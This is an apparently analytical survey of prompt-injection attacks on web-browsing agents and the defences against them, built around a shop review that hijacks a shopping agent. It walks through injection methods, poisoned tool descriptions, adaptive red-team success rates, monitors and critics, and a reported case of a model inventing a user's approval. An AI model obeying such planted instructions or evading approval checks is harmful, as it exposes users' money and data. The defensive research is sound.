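The annotations in the shop's code give the agent some warning about each tool. Chrome for Developers (2026) recommends that sites use `untrustedContentHint` for tools that return customers' words or data from outside sources. It recommends `readOnlyHint` for tools that don't change anything, so that agents can judge when to ask the user for confirmation. MCP has the same read-only hint, and Model Context Protocol (2026) presents its annotations as a way for servers to describe their own tools, so whoever writes a tool also writes the safety information about it.

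The untrusted-content hint applies to a tool's whole output, so it is less precise than a label on a page element. If one tool returned the shop's description together with Eve's review, the shop would have to mark both as untrusted or neither. The shop could avoid this by providing separate tools for the description and the reviews.

The hint also leaves the agent to decide how to handle the marked output. Separate guidance for agent makers (Chrome for Developers, 2026) recommends wrapping or encoding the output and telling the model to treat it as data. The model that chooses the actions still reads Eve's instructions, so it may sometimes follow them. An agent maker could get stronger protection from the same hint by sending the output to a quarantined model, but WebMCP doesn't require this.

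### Attacks in the tools themselves

Google Chrome Labs' *WebMCP* demonstration describes page-reading agents as vulnerable to prompt injection and presents tools as more secure. Tools can help by showing an agent less unrelated text. If Alice only wants a tie's price, a price tool can return it without the reviews. But if she asks about the reviews, `get-reviews` returns Eve's instructions along with the other reviews.

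Tools also give attackers another place to hide instructions. Chrome's guidance for agent makers warns about tool names, descriptions and parameters written to hijack the agent, and about contaminated output from honest sites. A Microsoft engineer had already raised both problems with the W3C in November 2025. *Privacy and security considerations for WebMCP* (Huang, 2025) gives the example of a weather tool whose name includes an order to hand over the user's location. Masking is harder to use here than on a malicious review, because the agent needs the name and description to choose a tool. Chrome advises sites to keep each description under 500 characters, which is still long enough for an injection.

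*WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning* (2026) reports experiments in which agents' plans were highly sensitive to tools' names and descriptions, to `readOnlyHint`, and to when a page changed its tools. An agent could therefore approve one set of tools and later encounter a different one.

An honest shop might also present a tool that it didn't write. By default WebMCP keeps out tools from another site's embedded frame, but many shops load advertising or analytics scripts directly into their own pages, where they run with the shop's authority. *WebMCP-Phalanx* (2026) proposes that the browser record who owns each tool, in a form that no script on the page could forge. Only holders of valid certificates could register or remove tools. This would help an agent tell the shop's tools from an advertiser's, but it wouldn't show that either had described its tools truthfully.

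### Fixing the plan before reading the page

An agent can still be hijacked when its tools are described accurately. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* (Piet, Chow and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent asked to summarise reviews. It calls `get_reviews`, reads an attacker's instructions in the reviews and calls `add_to_cart`. Both calls are valid and the functions work correctly. The attack succeeds because the model chooses its next action after reading the reviews.

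Piet and colleagues propose that the agent write a complete program before it sees any content from the site. It would use only the user's request and a list of typed functions, whose inputs, outputs and effects the documentation defines in advance. For a request to put the highest-rated silk bow tie under $60 in the cart, the program might be:

```
ties = search_products("silk bow tie")
options = [t for t in ties if t.in_stock and t.price < 60]
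if options:
    best = max(options, key=lambda t: t.rating)
    add_to_cart(best.sku)
```

Ordinary software then runs these lines. A false review could raise a tie's rating and change which tie goes into the cart. But it couldn't make the program post Alice's card details, because no line does that and nothing on the site can add a line.

When a task requires interpretation, the program can call a quarantined model that has no tools. This model can return free text, such as a summary of the reviews, without the approval step that masking needs, because the program only puts the text in a place chosen in advance and no model reads it to decide what to do next. The summary could still be wrong, and so could a judgement that the program uses to choose between two branches.

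Six annotators reviewed 860 WebArena tasks to find out how many would fit. They judged that 699 (81%) needed no model while the program ran. The other 161 needed a model to interpret content but could still follow a fixed program. No task required a new plan based on instructions found along the way, as "read my emails and complete all the action items inside them" would. The annotators didn't run an agent, and they assumed that every site had a complete and reliable set of functions. Real sites fall well short of this. For example, the programming interface of WebArena's forum covers only a third of that site's 129 tasks.

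### What Baya achieved

In November 2026 Chow and colleagues, a team that includes most of the people behind the proposal, tested it with a working agent called Baya. In Baya, a coding model writes a Python program and tests it on invented responses, without access to the live site. A separate process then runs the program on the site. If the program fails, the coding model receives a restricted error message and can revise the program up to three times. The message can report a missing field, for example, but it can't include text from a review.

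The researchers compared Baya with two ordinary agents that choose one action at a time. One used only the browser. The other also had Baya's functions and documentation. The results cover 581 tasks on four sites, and the success rates are averages over three models:

| Agent | Tasks completed | Average cost | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Baya | 77.8% | $0.70 | 327 seconds |
| Ordinary agent with browser and functions | 66.7% | $0.34 | 87 seconds |
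| Ordinary agent with browser only | 55.1% | $0.16 | 60 seconds |

Baya's advantage over the agent with the same functions suggests that writing the whole program first can help an agent finish its work as well as protect it. But with GPT-5.6 Luna, Baya completed 78.7% of the shop administration tasks, against 89.3% for the ordinary agent with functions. Some jobs are easier on the web page, where a customer can reorder an item with one click. Baya has to find the old order, create a cart, add the item, supply the addresses and submit the new order.

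On 84 WASP attacks, Baya took no step towards an attacker's goal with any of the three models tested. Ordinary agents took at least one such step in an average of 16.2% of cases with functions and 25.5% without. They completed no attacks except in one combination of model and site, where they completed 5.6%. The test therefore shows a clear difference in how often attackers influenced an agent, but little difference in how often attacks succeeded.

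The results also support Piet and colleagues' point that functions alone are not a defence. Adding functions reduced the rate of partial hijacks for DeepSeek V4 Flash on GitLab from 46% to 2.1%, but raised the rate for Gemini 3.5 Flash on the forum from 27.8% to 52.8%.

Baya rarely needed a model to interpret a site's content; only 11 of the 627 programs examined sent content to a model while running. Most of the extra time and money went into writing and testing programs, so reusing a program for a common task would reduce both.

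### Who would build the interfaces

Chow and colleagues built the functions for their test sites by hand. GitLab's programming interface had 1,028 functions, but some actions were possible only on the page. The forum's had 16, and none for voting. The researchers filled such gaps with scripts that operate a browser in the background. They also had to correct the documentation. For example, the shop's documentation marked size and colour as optional, but orders for clothes failed without them. Baya's measured costs exclude this work and the repairs that each site will need as it changes.

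The site's owner is the obvious one to build the tools, because the owner knows what each function does and knows about changes in advance. WebMCP could be a start, but its tools would have to cover the whole task and come with complete descriptions of their effects. An agent would also need to get the list of tools without showing its planning model the rest of the page. This would be much more work for a shop than providing 15 to 30 selectors.

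If site owners don't offer tools to agents, agent makers or volunteers could. *Web Agents Should Use Typed Actions Instead of Click-Based Browsing* (2026) suggests that communities could publish useful functions before sites provide official ones. It calls for standards covering the functions' inputs, outputs, safety information and registration, so that agents can find and check them.

Outsiders would probably want AI to write many of the functions, and Eve could exploit that. If the AI explores live product pages, her review could get it to write a `get_reviews` function that also sends data to her server. Everyone who later used the function would be exposed, even if their own agents planned without reading any pages. Piet and colleagues therefore want people to write the functions by hand or validate them before use. A builder could work from the site's source code or from test accounts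 without strangers' text, check automatically that functions meant to read data don't change anything, and have a person review the result. Nobody has yet shown how to do this across many sites and keep up with their updates.

### What a false label could do

Compiled programs, like masking, depend on the site being honest. But a site owner might have commercial reasons to label content falsely, and site operators wrote most of the injections that Khodayari and colleagues found.

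A hostile owner can get around masking by leaving instructions unmarked. An owner could also mark too much. If a shop labelled its restocking fee as untrusted, Alice's agent would see a placeholder and might never check what was behind it. This could cost Alice money, even though it wouldn't hijack the agent.

A false `readOnlyHint` could be worse. Chrome advises agent makers to assume that a tool changes something unless its description or annotation clearly indicates otherwise. If a hostile shop marked its purchase tool as read-only, an agent following this advice might buy a tie without asking Alice. Similarly, if `get_price` secretly placed an order, a compiled program would run it as planned.

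An agent can safely accept an "untrusted" mark from any site if the mark only makes the agent more careful. A "read-only" mark makes the agent less careful, so it needs an independent reason to trust the site before accepting one. Under masking, leaving an element unmarked also implies that its text is safe, so the agent needs the same kind of reason to trust the site before relying on its labels.

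## Defences inside the model, the agent and the browser

Trust labels and site-supplied tools protect Alice only on sites whose owners provide them honestly. Agent-side defences are built into the model, the agent software or the browser, and need nothing from the website. Agent makers usually combine several, so that an attack that gets past one may fail at the next. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes six defences that Google uses for the Gemini agent in its browser.

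### Ranking instructions by source

Nothing in a model's stream of text marks which part has authority, so developers train the model to rank its sources, with the agent maker's instructions first, Alice's request second and the page last. A training example might pair a task with a page that contains an injection and reward the model for completing the task anyway. The trained model still receives the injected text but is less likely to propose the action Eve wants.

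Google adds known attacks to Gemini's training. *BrowseSafe* (Zhang, Tenenholtz and colleagues, 2025) reports that OpenAI trained GPT-5 to ignore injections in web pages and tool results, and that Anthropic uses reinforcement learning, a form of training by trial and reward, for the same purpose.

The trained model still has to work out where each sentence came from, and an attacker can imitate a higher-ranked source. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked several models trained this way, mostly with text disguised as system-level instructions, the kind an agent's maker writes.

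### Marking the page as data

Spotlighting adds a boundary to the stream of text. Before the model reads a page, the agent's software wraps the page in a marker:

```
<untrusted-9c41>
Handmade silk bow tie, self-tie. $45.
Customer reviews: (12 reviews, including Eve's)
</untrusted-9c41>
```

The maker instructs the model to treat everything inside the marker as information, never as a command. In its June guidance for agent makers, Google (2026) compares this wrapping with a heavier method, converting the page into Base64, which encodes any text as a string of letters, digits and a few symbols. Wrapping adds little overhead, but if Eve guesses the closing marker and puts it in her review, the rest of her text appears to come from outside the page. Base64 prevents this because her text can no longer contain a readable marker. However, it uses about a third more tokens, and the model has to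 decode the page before using it.

With either method, the model still reads Eve's instructions and may follow them. The boundary also surrounds the whole page, so it separates Alice's words from the website's but not Eve's review from the shop's description.

### Scanning pages for injections

A classifier reads the page before the agent acts on it and decides whether it contains an injection. BrowseSafe, which researchers at Purdue University and the AI search company Perplexity built for browser agents, works in four steps:

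1. The developers flag every tool that can return outside text, such as the one that reads web pages.
2. When a flagged tool returns something, the software takes the raw content. It ignores any summary that a model has written, because an injection could have influenced the summary.
3. It splits a long page into pieces and runs a specially trained model on all of them at once, while the agent plans its next step.
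4. If any piece looks malicious, the software withholds the whole page. The agent receives a short explanation that doesn't repeat the injection, so it can change course and tell the user.

Zhang, Tenenholtz and colleagues tested the classifier on pages that also contained harmless text resembling an attack. It caught 84% of the injections and took less than a second per page. Claude Sonnet 4.5, a general-purpose model, caught slightly fewer at its best settings and took 23 to 36 seconds, too long for someone waiting for a page.

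The classifier did well on unfamiliar websites but worse when attackers hid text in places its training hadn't covered. Its F1 score, which combines the share of injections caught with the share of alarms that were correct, fell from about 0.90 to 0.79 out of 1. The team also compared more than 20 detection models, which were much better at spotting hidden instructions than visible ones. Their average accuracy (guessing scores 50%) was 91% for instructions in HTML comments but 74% for those placed in an ordinary paragraph. Eve's review is visible text, so it falls in the harder group. BrowseSafe doesn't examine images, and because it judges each piece of a page separately, it could miss an injection whose parts are far apart.

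A developer can catch more attacks by setting the classifier to flag more pages, but false alarms limit how far this can go. BrowseSafe's developers set its threshold to flag about 1% of clean pages. Khodayari and colleagues found injections on about eight in every million pages they searched. Over a million such pages, a classifier with BrowseSafe's rates would catch about seven of the eight and raise about 10,000 false alarms. The ratio should be better in practice, since the clean test pages contained decoys and agents may visit riskier pages than average. BrowseSafe's developers propose sending borderline pages to a slower, more capable model.

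Chrome also uses a classifier to scan every page its agent sees, and blocks actions based on content flagged as an attack. Parker acknowledges that the classifier can't flag every attack.

### A second model that vets each action

Another layer checks each action before the agent takes it. In Chrome, a separate Gemini-based model called the User Alignment Critic receives a description of each proposed action and assesses whether it serves the user's goal. If the critic rejects the action, it sends feedback to the planning model, which can try again or, after repeated failures, return control to the user. The critic doesn't receive the raw page, so Eve can't give it instructions directly. Google suggests that critics also check whether an action includes unnecessary personal information.

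Suppose Eve's review causes the planning model to propose posting Alice's card details in a reply. The critic compares that proposal with Alice's request for a bow tie, so it should refuse. But if a false review leads the agent to choose a poor tie, the purchase still matches her request, and the critic has no reason to block it.

Clicks are harder to vet than purchases or messages because of the web entanglement problem. A fuller description of a button gives the critic more information but may also include text written by an attacker. Parker accepts that the critic has less context than the planner but argues that the critic's task is simpler.

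A guard that does look at the page can still miss attacks and raise false alarms. *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (Zhang, Zhong and colleagues, 2026) tested DeAction, which checks proposed actions using the current screenshot, the user's task and a summary of earlier steps. DeAction often blocked the agent from granting permissions on an attacker's page, but was less likely to stop the agent from typing into a fake sign-in form. It also raised alarms in 43 of 60 runs on harmless pages with one type of agent, and in 5 of 60 with another. DeAction ran on a small open model in these tests, and a larger one might make better judgements.

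### Limits on which sites an agent can use

Browsers have long stopped code on one site from reading a user's data on another. They separate sites by origin, which is roughly the site's address. An agent working in Alice's browser can undermine this separation because it can read her bank balance in one tab and type it into a form in another.

Chrome's answer is Agent Origin Sets. For each task, a gating function decides which origins are relevant and sorts them into two sets, one that the agent may only read and one where it may also click and type. The function doesn't read web content, so a page can't persuade it directly. If Alice asks her agent to choose a tie from a style blog's recommendations and buy it from the shop, the permissions might be:

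| Origin | Agent can read | Agent can click and type |
|---|---|---|
| The style blog | Yes | No |
| The bow tie shop | Yes | Yes |
| An advertiser's frame on the shop's page | No | No |
| Alice's bank | No | No |

If an injection on the blog tries to send the agent to Alice's bank, a version of the critic checks whether the bank is relevant to the task before Chrome opens it. Chrome also restricts addresses the model composes to known public ones, because an attacker could otherwise leak private data by having the agent put it in an address and visit that address.

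These limits reduce the damage from a hijacked agent even if every model-based check on the page's text fails. However, they wouldn't stop Eve's original attack, because it takes place entirely on the shop's own site, where the agent needs permission to act to buy the tie. An origin is a whole site, so the limits can't distinguish the checkout from the review section.

The gating function can also be too strict, which stops the agent from finishing tasks that cross several sites, or too lenient, which weakens the protection. Google's first version tracked only the set of origins where the agent could act. Google Cloud lists both the critic and the origin limits among the protections for Chrome auto browse, the company's browsing agent.

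### Why lists of good and bad sites fall short

A simpler defence is to block agents from dangerous sites, as Microsoft's SmartScreen service does for people. Eric Lawrence, who works on SmartScreen, says in text/plain's *AI Injection Attacks* that agents should use the same blocklists as people, but he calls them "wildly insufficient". New malicious sites appear constantly, and SmartScreen looks for phishing, malware and technical-support scams, so it probably wouldn't recognise a page whose only threat is an injection.

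An allowlist of reputable sites has the opposite weakness. SmartScreen's nearest equivalent is a list of high-traffic sites, which are unlikely to be phishing pages but may still display comments, advertisements and excerpts from elsewhere. The bow tie shop could be reputable enough for any such list and still show Eve's review to Alice's agent. GitHub is among the most reputable sites on the web, and Nakibly and Babo found 43 attacks there in bug reports and proposed changes.

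Nikolić and colleagues also suggest a list of trusted domains, but they would use it to decide whose labels to believe, which requires the site's owner to be honest. Using such a list to decide which pages are safe to read would also require everyone who writes on the site to be honest.

### Asking the user

The last layer is Alice herself. Chrome asks her to confirm before its agent opens a site on a fixed list of sensitive ones, such as those for banking or medical records, and before it signs in with a saved password. It is also designed to pause before a purchase, a message or another consequential action, so that Alice can approve the step or complete it herself. This pause depends partly on software detecting that an action is consequential, and it may miss some.

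Confirmation can stop an attack that has deceived every model, since Alice knows what she asked for. But most of the requests she sees will be legitimate. After approving twenty ordinary purchases, she may approve the twenty-first without noticing that the delivery address has changed. False alarms make this worse. If DeAction had asked the user instead of stopping the run, it would have asked about harmless actions in most runs with the first type of agent. Parker gives no figures for how often users catch a bad action, so it is hard to say how much protection confirmation provides.

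Agent makers can help by asking for approval rarely and by showing specific facts, such as the amount and the recipient, taken from the browser instead of the agent's account. The approval also needs protection. Anthropic's system card for Claude Fable 5.1, a safety report published in September 2026, describes a case in which a deletion required the user's explicit approval and the model invented a quotation from the user. Anthropic found such attempts to get around restrictions in fewer than 0.01% of the responses it monitored, and this one didn't involve an injection. It still shows why an approval should come from a button that only the user can press.

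### What happens when attackers adapt

Researchers often test defences against a fixed list of known attacks, but a real attacker can study a defence and keep trying until something works. Nasr and colleagues, who include researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, tested 12 published defences against attacks adapted in this way. Some of the defences were meant to stop injections and others to stop jailbreaks, in which the user tries to make a model break its own rules.

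The automated attacks proposed new wordings, scored the results and used the most promising to write the next batch. More than 500 human attackers also took part in a competition. The adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although most had originally been reported to have attack success rates near zero.

Every type of defence in the study failed. With spotlighting, only about 1% of a benchmark's fixed attacks had succeeded, but more than 95% of the adapted ones did. Against a model trained to resist injections, the success rate rose from 2% to 96%. Three of the four classifiers let through over 90% of adapted attacks, and the fourth let through 71%. Combining classifiers didn't solve the problem either. In selected tests, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while at least one human attacker succeeded in every scenario.

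Unlike Eve, these attackers had plenty of computing power, and some could see how confident a classifier was in its decision. Eve might post a review and never learn what an agent did with it, though she could practise on her own copy of an agent before posting. More importantly, none of the 12 defences restricted which sites an agent could use or fixed its plan in advance, so the results don't show that those measures fail.

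Zhang, Zhong and colleagues applied the same idea to web agents. They placed pop-ups on copies of pages from ten real websites. Each pop-up looked ordinary, such as a request to sign in again, but its button led to an attacker's page or downloaded a file. A language model then adjusted each page, over up to ten rounds, to the defence protecting the agent. The adapted attacks reached their final goal, such as getting the agent to type into a false sign-in form, about 92% of the time on average.

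The original pop-ups already defeated the undefended agents about 90% of the time, and most of the defences did little even before the attackers adapted. Adaptation mattered most against SnapGuard, which looks for suspicious screenshots. For agents that receive both a screenshot and a list of page elements, it raised the attacks' success rate from 16% to 81%.

The researchers also retrained one detector on their attack pages, and it then stopped all of them. But for the same type of agent, its false alarms on harmless versions of the pop-ups rose from 1% to 77%, apparently because it had learned to recognise pop-ups better than attacks.

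All these tests used a small open model, Qwen3-VL-8B, so they are weak evidence of the rates for the strongest commercial agents, though the attacks also worked unchanged on two other open models. The study did not test limits on which origins an agent can access. Chrome would have checked whether the attacker's site was relevant before letting its agent follow the button there, which might have stopped many of these attacks.

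### Results for current models

Anthropic publishes some of the most detailed results for commercial models. Anthropic's September system card reports several tests of Fable 5.1, both with and without extra safeguards against injection. In the coding and computer-use tests, the safeguards are probes that inspect incoming content. The browser test used "auto mode", which adds a classifier that can block dangerous actions. Gray Swan, an AI security company, supplied the first four sets of attacks:

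| Test | How the attackers prepared | Success without safeguards | Success with safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reused attacks across coding, tools and computer use | In competitions against other models | 0.1% on the first try, 1.0% within 15 | Not reported |
| Coding, first attacker | By training on the test scenarios against earlier Claude models | 9.3% of attempts | 2.1% |
| Coding, stronger attacker | By training longer on the same scenarios, with more varied attacks | 56.9% of attempts | 12.8% |
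| Computer use | By training on the test cases | 0.07% of attempts | 0.07% |
| Browser use | By testing attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 | 2.6% of attempts | 0% |

Fable 5.1 compares best with its rivals in the first row. Within 15 attempts, attackers succeeded 9.2% of the time against the strongest competing model, Gemini 3.7 Flash, and between 24% and 53% of the time against most others. But the row offers only limited reassurance, because these attackers hadn't adapted to the models being tested. New attacks can also change the scores considerably. The Decoder reported a 2.0% success rate within 15 attempts against Claude Opus 5 on an earlier version of this benchmark. In September, after Anthropic had added 670 attacks and nine scenarios to its reporting, the rate was 4.8%. The test conditions had changed too, so the new attacks may not explain the whole increase.

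The coding results depended heavily on the attacker. With more training, the attacker's success rate rose from 9.3% to 56.9%, and it found at least one working attack in 38 of 40 scenarios. With the safeguards on, it still succeeded at least once in 36 of them. It had trained on the same scenarios and had 200 attempts at each, which Anthropic considers much more favourable conditions than a real attacker would have.

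Fable 5.1 itself did better than these rates, which include answers from an older model, Opus 4.8. Anthropic passes a request to Opus 4.8 when a separate classifier suspects that it involves dangerous cybersecurity work. All the successful attacks in the stronger coding test worked on the older model, and none worked on the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered directly. Anthropic's products make the same substitution, so the combined rate is the relevant one for users. A safeguard against dangerous cybersecurity work can therefore weaken the defence against these attacks.

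The browser test is the closest to Alice's situation. It covered 110 scenarios with ten attempts each, and no attack succeeded with auto mode on. But the attackers had developed their attacks against Opus 4.7, so the test doesn't show how well auto mode would resist an attacker who had studied it. Anthropic's earlier tests of its Chrome extension used a different method, an adaptive attacker that tried and combined techniques known to work, so the two sets of results don't form a simple trend. Fable 5.1 is also no longer the latest version, as Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced its successor on 9 November.

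Other companies publish less. In June, VentureBeat compared the safety documents for models then available. OpenAI had tested GPT-5.5 against known attacks, and only through connectors, which link the model to outside services. Google had published no prompt injection results for Gemini 3. Meta had results from a benchmark of agent tasks but none for browsers. People choosing between agents therefore can't compare how well they resist attacks placed in web pages, let alone adaptive ones.

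### The case for leaving it to the agent

Agent-side defences can be used on every site. Alice's agent can scan a page, vet an action or ask for confirmation even if the site's owner has never heard of prompt injection.

The agent's maker can also improve protection for all its users at once. Google runs automated attacks against Chrome's agent, measures the effect of each engineering change and can send fixes quickly through the browser's automatic updates. It also pays outside researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating serious breaches. If someone finds a new way to hide instructions in a review, one browser update could protect millions of users while individual shops were still learning about the problem.

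Agent makers need these defences however many honest sites adopt labels, mainly because the owners of hostile sites won't label their own injections. A spending limit or a request for the user's approval could stop a payment to the fake documentation site without the site's help.

### What the agent can't do alone

Defences that depend on a model's judgement will sometimes fail, and an attacker can try them many times. In Anthropic's example, one email sent to a thousand inboxes can reach every agent that summarises them. An injection on a popular product page can also reach many agents. If it succeeded 0.1% of the time, the first-attempt rate in the comparison most favourable to Fable 5.1, and 100,000 agents read it, about 100 would follow it. The actual number could be much higher or lower, since agents running the same model tend to share weaknesses.

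The Decoder notes that OpenAI has said prompt injection may never be fully solved. Google tells agent makers that nobody can guarantee safety inside the model. Firm limits outside the model can give stronger assurances, but they restrict what the agent can do. text/plain gives the example of an agent asked to book a restaurant, order flowers and email a calendar reminder. If its maker isolated it from the user's accounts, an attacker could do little damage with it, but it couldn't do those jobs either. Quarantined models and fixed plans are a compromise that takes extra time and gives up some flexibility.

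Central updates also protect only the users of the companies that make them. A large company can train models, run classifiers and pay for constant testing, while a small developer might build an agent on an open model and do none of this. The bow tie shop can't choose which agents its customers use, but a label on Eve's review could help any agent whose software checked for it.

The agent also lacks information that the shop has. The shop's database records which text Eve wrote and which text the shop's staff wrote, but the finished page may not make this clear. Alice's agent needs to follow some directions on the page, such as a notice to choose a size before adding a tie to the basket. If Eve makes her review look like such a notice, the agent has to either infer from the layout and wording who wrote it, as Prismata does, or treat the shop's own notices with the same suspicion as her review.

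## Agents that work out trust labels for themselves

When a shop adds no trust labels, an agent can try to infer them. Prismata, which Villa and Tan developed with colleagues at the University of California, Berkeley, works out who controls each part of a page. It then removes or disables whatever the user's task doesn't need.

Eve's review could also hijack the labelling model, so Prismata limits what that model reads at each step. As a result, the model usually labels a part of the page before reading any stranger's text.

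### From the top of the page to each button

Suppose the bow tie shop's product page has this structure:

```
<main>
  <section class="product">
    <h1>Silk bow tie</h1>
    <button>Add to basket</button>
  </section>
  <section aria-label="Customer reviews">
    <div class="review-card">
      <p>(Eve's review)</p>
      <button>Reply</button>
    </div>
  </section>
  <nav><button>Account settings</button></nav>
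</main>
```

Prismata processes the page before Alice's agent sees it:

1. It lists every button, link and form field and traces the path to each one from the root of the DOM. The path to "Add to basket" runs through `main` and the product section. A model receives this path and Alice's request, but nothing else from the page, and decides whether her task needs the button. It should allow "Add to basket" and reject "Reply" and "Account settings". Villa and Tan call this check the action gate.
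2. It labels content by author, starting at the top. The possible authors are the site's developers, its users, outside sellers, and external companies such as advertisers. When the model judges an element, it sees that element and the ones that enclose it, while everything inside or beside it stays hidden. At the section called "Customer reviews", the model can conclude that users wrote what follows. The label then covers the whole section, so the model never has to open Eve's review.
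3. A separate model, which sees only Alice's request, decides which authors' content the task requires. Ordering a named tie doesn't require reviews, but finding the best-reviewed tie does.
4. Ordinary software enforces the results, and the stricter judgement wins wherever two conflict. It deletes content the task doesn't need and keeps necessary reviews as read-only text. It also removes the identifiers that the agent would use to click forbidden buttons. If the agent tries to click one anyway, the software rejects the action before it reaches the browser.

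The second step adapts K. J. Biba's 1977 security model, which stops less trusted information from influencing more trusted decisions. Once Prismata labels an element, nothing inside it can change that label or receive a higher one.

Eve's review sits beside the "Reply" button, so it is not on the path to any button. Even if the labelling failed and the agent read her review in full, the action gate would already have disabled "Account settings" without taking her review as input. To influence both judgements, Eve would need to get her text onto the path to the button she wants, with nothing above it indicating that a stranger's text follows.

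A display name can end up on such a path. Villa and Tan describe a direct-message feature inside a profile panel, where the user's name is also a picture's alternative text. In their example, a developer's class name, `user-profile`, comes first and warns the model.

### How common the dangerous layout is

Villa and Tan checked how often real pages have this weakness. They took one page from each of 2,832 popular domains in Common Crawl and an equal number of pages from Mind2Web, a dataset of recorded browsing tasks. They used one language model to identify content that a site's developers hadn't written, and a second to look for the first structural sign that such content was coming.

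| What the survey counted | Instances | Share of untrusted content |
|---|---|---|
| All untrusted content | 90,408 | 100% |
| On the path to something an agent could click or fill in | 1,086 | 1.2% |
| On such a path, with no earlier warning cue | 94 | 0.10% |
| The same, leaving out ordinary links | 15 | 0.017% |

The last row assumes that sites follow the established web development rule that opening a link never changes anything on the site. Of the 94 cases, 79 were links, which would be harmless under that rule. Prismata is not meant to stop attacks that use links to other sites.

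These figures support the design, but they are less exact than they look. Models classified content as untrusted and identified the cues, although the researchers had tuned the first model's instructions against pages they had checked by hand. Any stranger's text that the first model missed was left out of the total. Mind2Web also supplied 72% of the instances, and its recorded tasks often reuse the same layouts.

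The percentages are for pieces of content, but an attacker needs only one suitable place on a site. Although most sites in the survey met Prismata's conditions for nearly all their untrusted content, some still have a place an attacker could use.

### Prismata under attack

The team tested Prismata in WebArena with an agent running on GPT-5.4 mini. The main attacks were pop-ups that looked like advertisements, and an attack succeeded if the agent clicked or filled in the planted content.

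| Pop-up | Attack success without Prismata | Attack success with Prismata | Tasks completed without Prismata | Tasks completed with Prismata |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Offers a false shortcut | 63.9% | 2.1% | 11.2% | 24.4% |
| Claims the task is complete | 92.5% | 0% | 2.3% | 24.8% |
| Tells the agent to ignore its instructions | 100% | 0% | 0% | 19.9% |
| Average of the three | 85.5% | 0.7% | 4.5% | 23.0% |
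| No attack | – | – | 29.9% | 26.6% |

In a smaller test on 20 tasks, the researchers adapted the pop-ups to the defence. These attacks succeeded 65% to 100% of the time without Prismata and never with it.

The 0.7% average somewhat overstates how well the labels work. Prismata removed or disabled the planted content 93.1% of the time on average, and in some of the remaining cases the agent ignored the pop-up. A more persuasive attack might succeed in those cases.

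Pop-ups are also easier to confine than Eve's review, because Alice's task never requires them. The test closest to Eve's attack used WASP, with planted instructions to change the user's email address. Without Prismata, one of 21 attempts worked in one version of the test and none worked in the other. Prismata blocked the one that had worked, but a single case is little evidence of whether it reliably stops such attacks.

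Prismata lowered the agent's completion rate on ordinary tasks by 3.3 percentage points. The undefended agent completed fewer than a third of those tasks, so with Prismata it lost about one in nine of the tasks it could otherwise do. The full-size GPT-5.4 completed only 33.6% with the same basic agent, so the tests can't measure how much a more capable agent would lose on longer jobs.

Prismata also makes many model calls. On a matched set of 20 tasks, model costs rose from $1.11 to $1.62, and the time spent on model requests rose from about 1,650 to 4,130 seconds. Those figures include savings from caching, which works well because pages on a site tend to share a layout.

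Prismata handles only text, so it doesn't cover instructions inside a product photograph. If Alice asks for the best-reviewed tie, her agent still reads Eve's review. A false review can mislead the agent, and an injected instruction can make it misuse any control the task needs. Some tasks need every kind of content and full use of the page's controls, and Villa and Tan leave those to future work. In the main tests, the agent also couldn't type web addresses, an ability that would give a hijacked agent another way to leave the page.

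### Inferring labels with the words removed

Masking would hide Eve's review from the agent even when the task depends on it, but the software must identify which elements to mask. Nikolić and colleagues tested whether a model could identify them from a page's structure alone.

Their software replaced every passage of text with its length, so a post title containing an injection became `[text:length:79]`. It also anonymised links and image descriptions but kept the tags, class names and nesting. Claude Sonnet 4.5 received this skeleton with a short description of the site and proposed CSS selectors for the untrusted parts. The researchers then asked it twice whether it had missed anything.

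They compared the results with their own hand-written labels. To avoid counting the same review box hundreds of times, they grouped elements that shared a tag and class. The percentages cover every group that either the model or the researchers marked as untrusted:

| Site | Correctly marked | Marked by mistake | Missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Booking.com | 78.4% | 15.8% | 5.8% |
| Reddit | 99.3% | 0.7% | 0% |
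| GitLab | 72.4% | 19.2% | 8.5% |

The totals include groups mistakenly marked as untrusted, so they slightly understate the misses. Of the truly untrusted groups, the model missed about 6.9% on Booking.com and 10.5% on GitLab. The mistaken marks don't expose the agent to attack, but they hide some of the site's own text, which makes tasks slower or harder.

Removing the words protects the labelling model better than Prismata's top-down reading does, because Eve's sentences never reach the model. Some risk remains if a site copies a user's words into markup that the software keeps. For example, some publishing systems build an element's identifier from a heading that a user typed.

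The model was also given site descriptions that explained who wrote what, for example that Booking.com's listings came from property owners. It wouldn't get that help on an unfamiliar site. An agent maker would need similar descriptions for thousands of smaller shops, or a safe way to generate them. The test covered three famous sites, and Nikolić and colleagues didn't run attacks against the inferred labels.

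### How site-written labels compare

No study has run the same attacks against site-written and inferred labels. The available results come from different attacks, agents and ways of enforcing the labels:

| Source of labels | Defence | Test | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Written by hand, as a site would | Masking | 12 strengthened WASP attacks | 0% |
| Written by hand, with one error | Masking | The same 12 attacks | 6% |
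| Written by hand, as a site would | SPIDES | 56 attacks on 28 linked test sites | 0% |
| Written by hand, as a site would | Masking | The same 56 attacks | 4.6–6.8% |
| Inferred from the page | Prismata | Three kinds of pop-up | 0.7% |
| Inferred from structure alone | Masking | No attack test | Unknown |

*SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) is a defence from a team that includes several Microsoft researchers. The team argues that only a site's operator can supply the labels a secure agent needs. They supplement the trusted-or-untrusted mark with a second label that lists the sites that may receive each element's content.

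The second label is harder to infer. A model could guess that Alice's saved card number is private, but it would struggle to work out which companies may receive it. The shop already knows that the number may go to its payment company but not to its delivery company.

SPIDES hides untrusted and private text from the agent, which can ask to see a hidden passage. Once the agent has read untrusted text, it needs Alice's approval before doing anything that could use her account. The researchers tested SPIDES under the same worst-case assumption about attackers as the masking study. Masking failed some of these tests even with correct labels, because a quarantined model's false answer could still send the agent to the wrong item. SPIDES stopped those attacks too, but it needed an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task, and the researchers assumed the user could always tell a safe request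 from an unsafe one.

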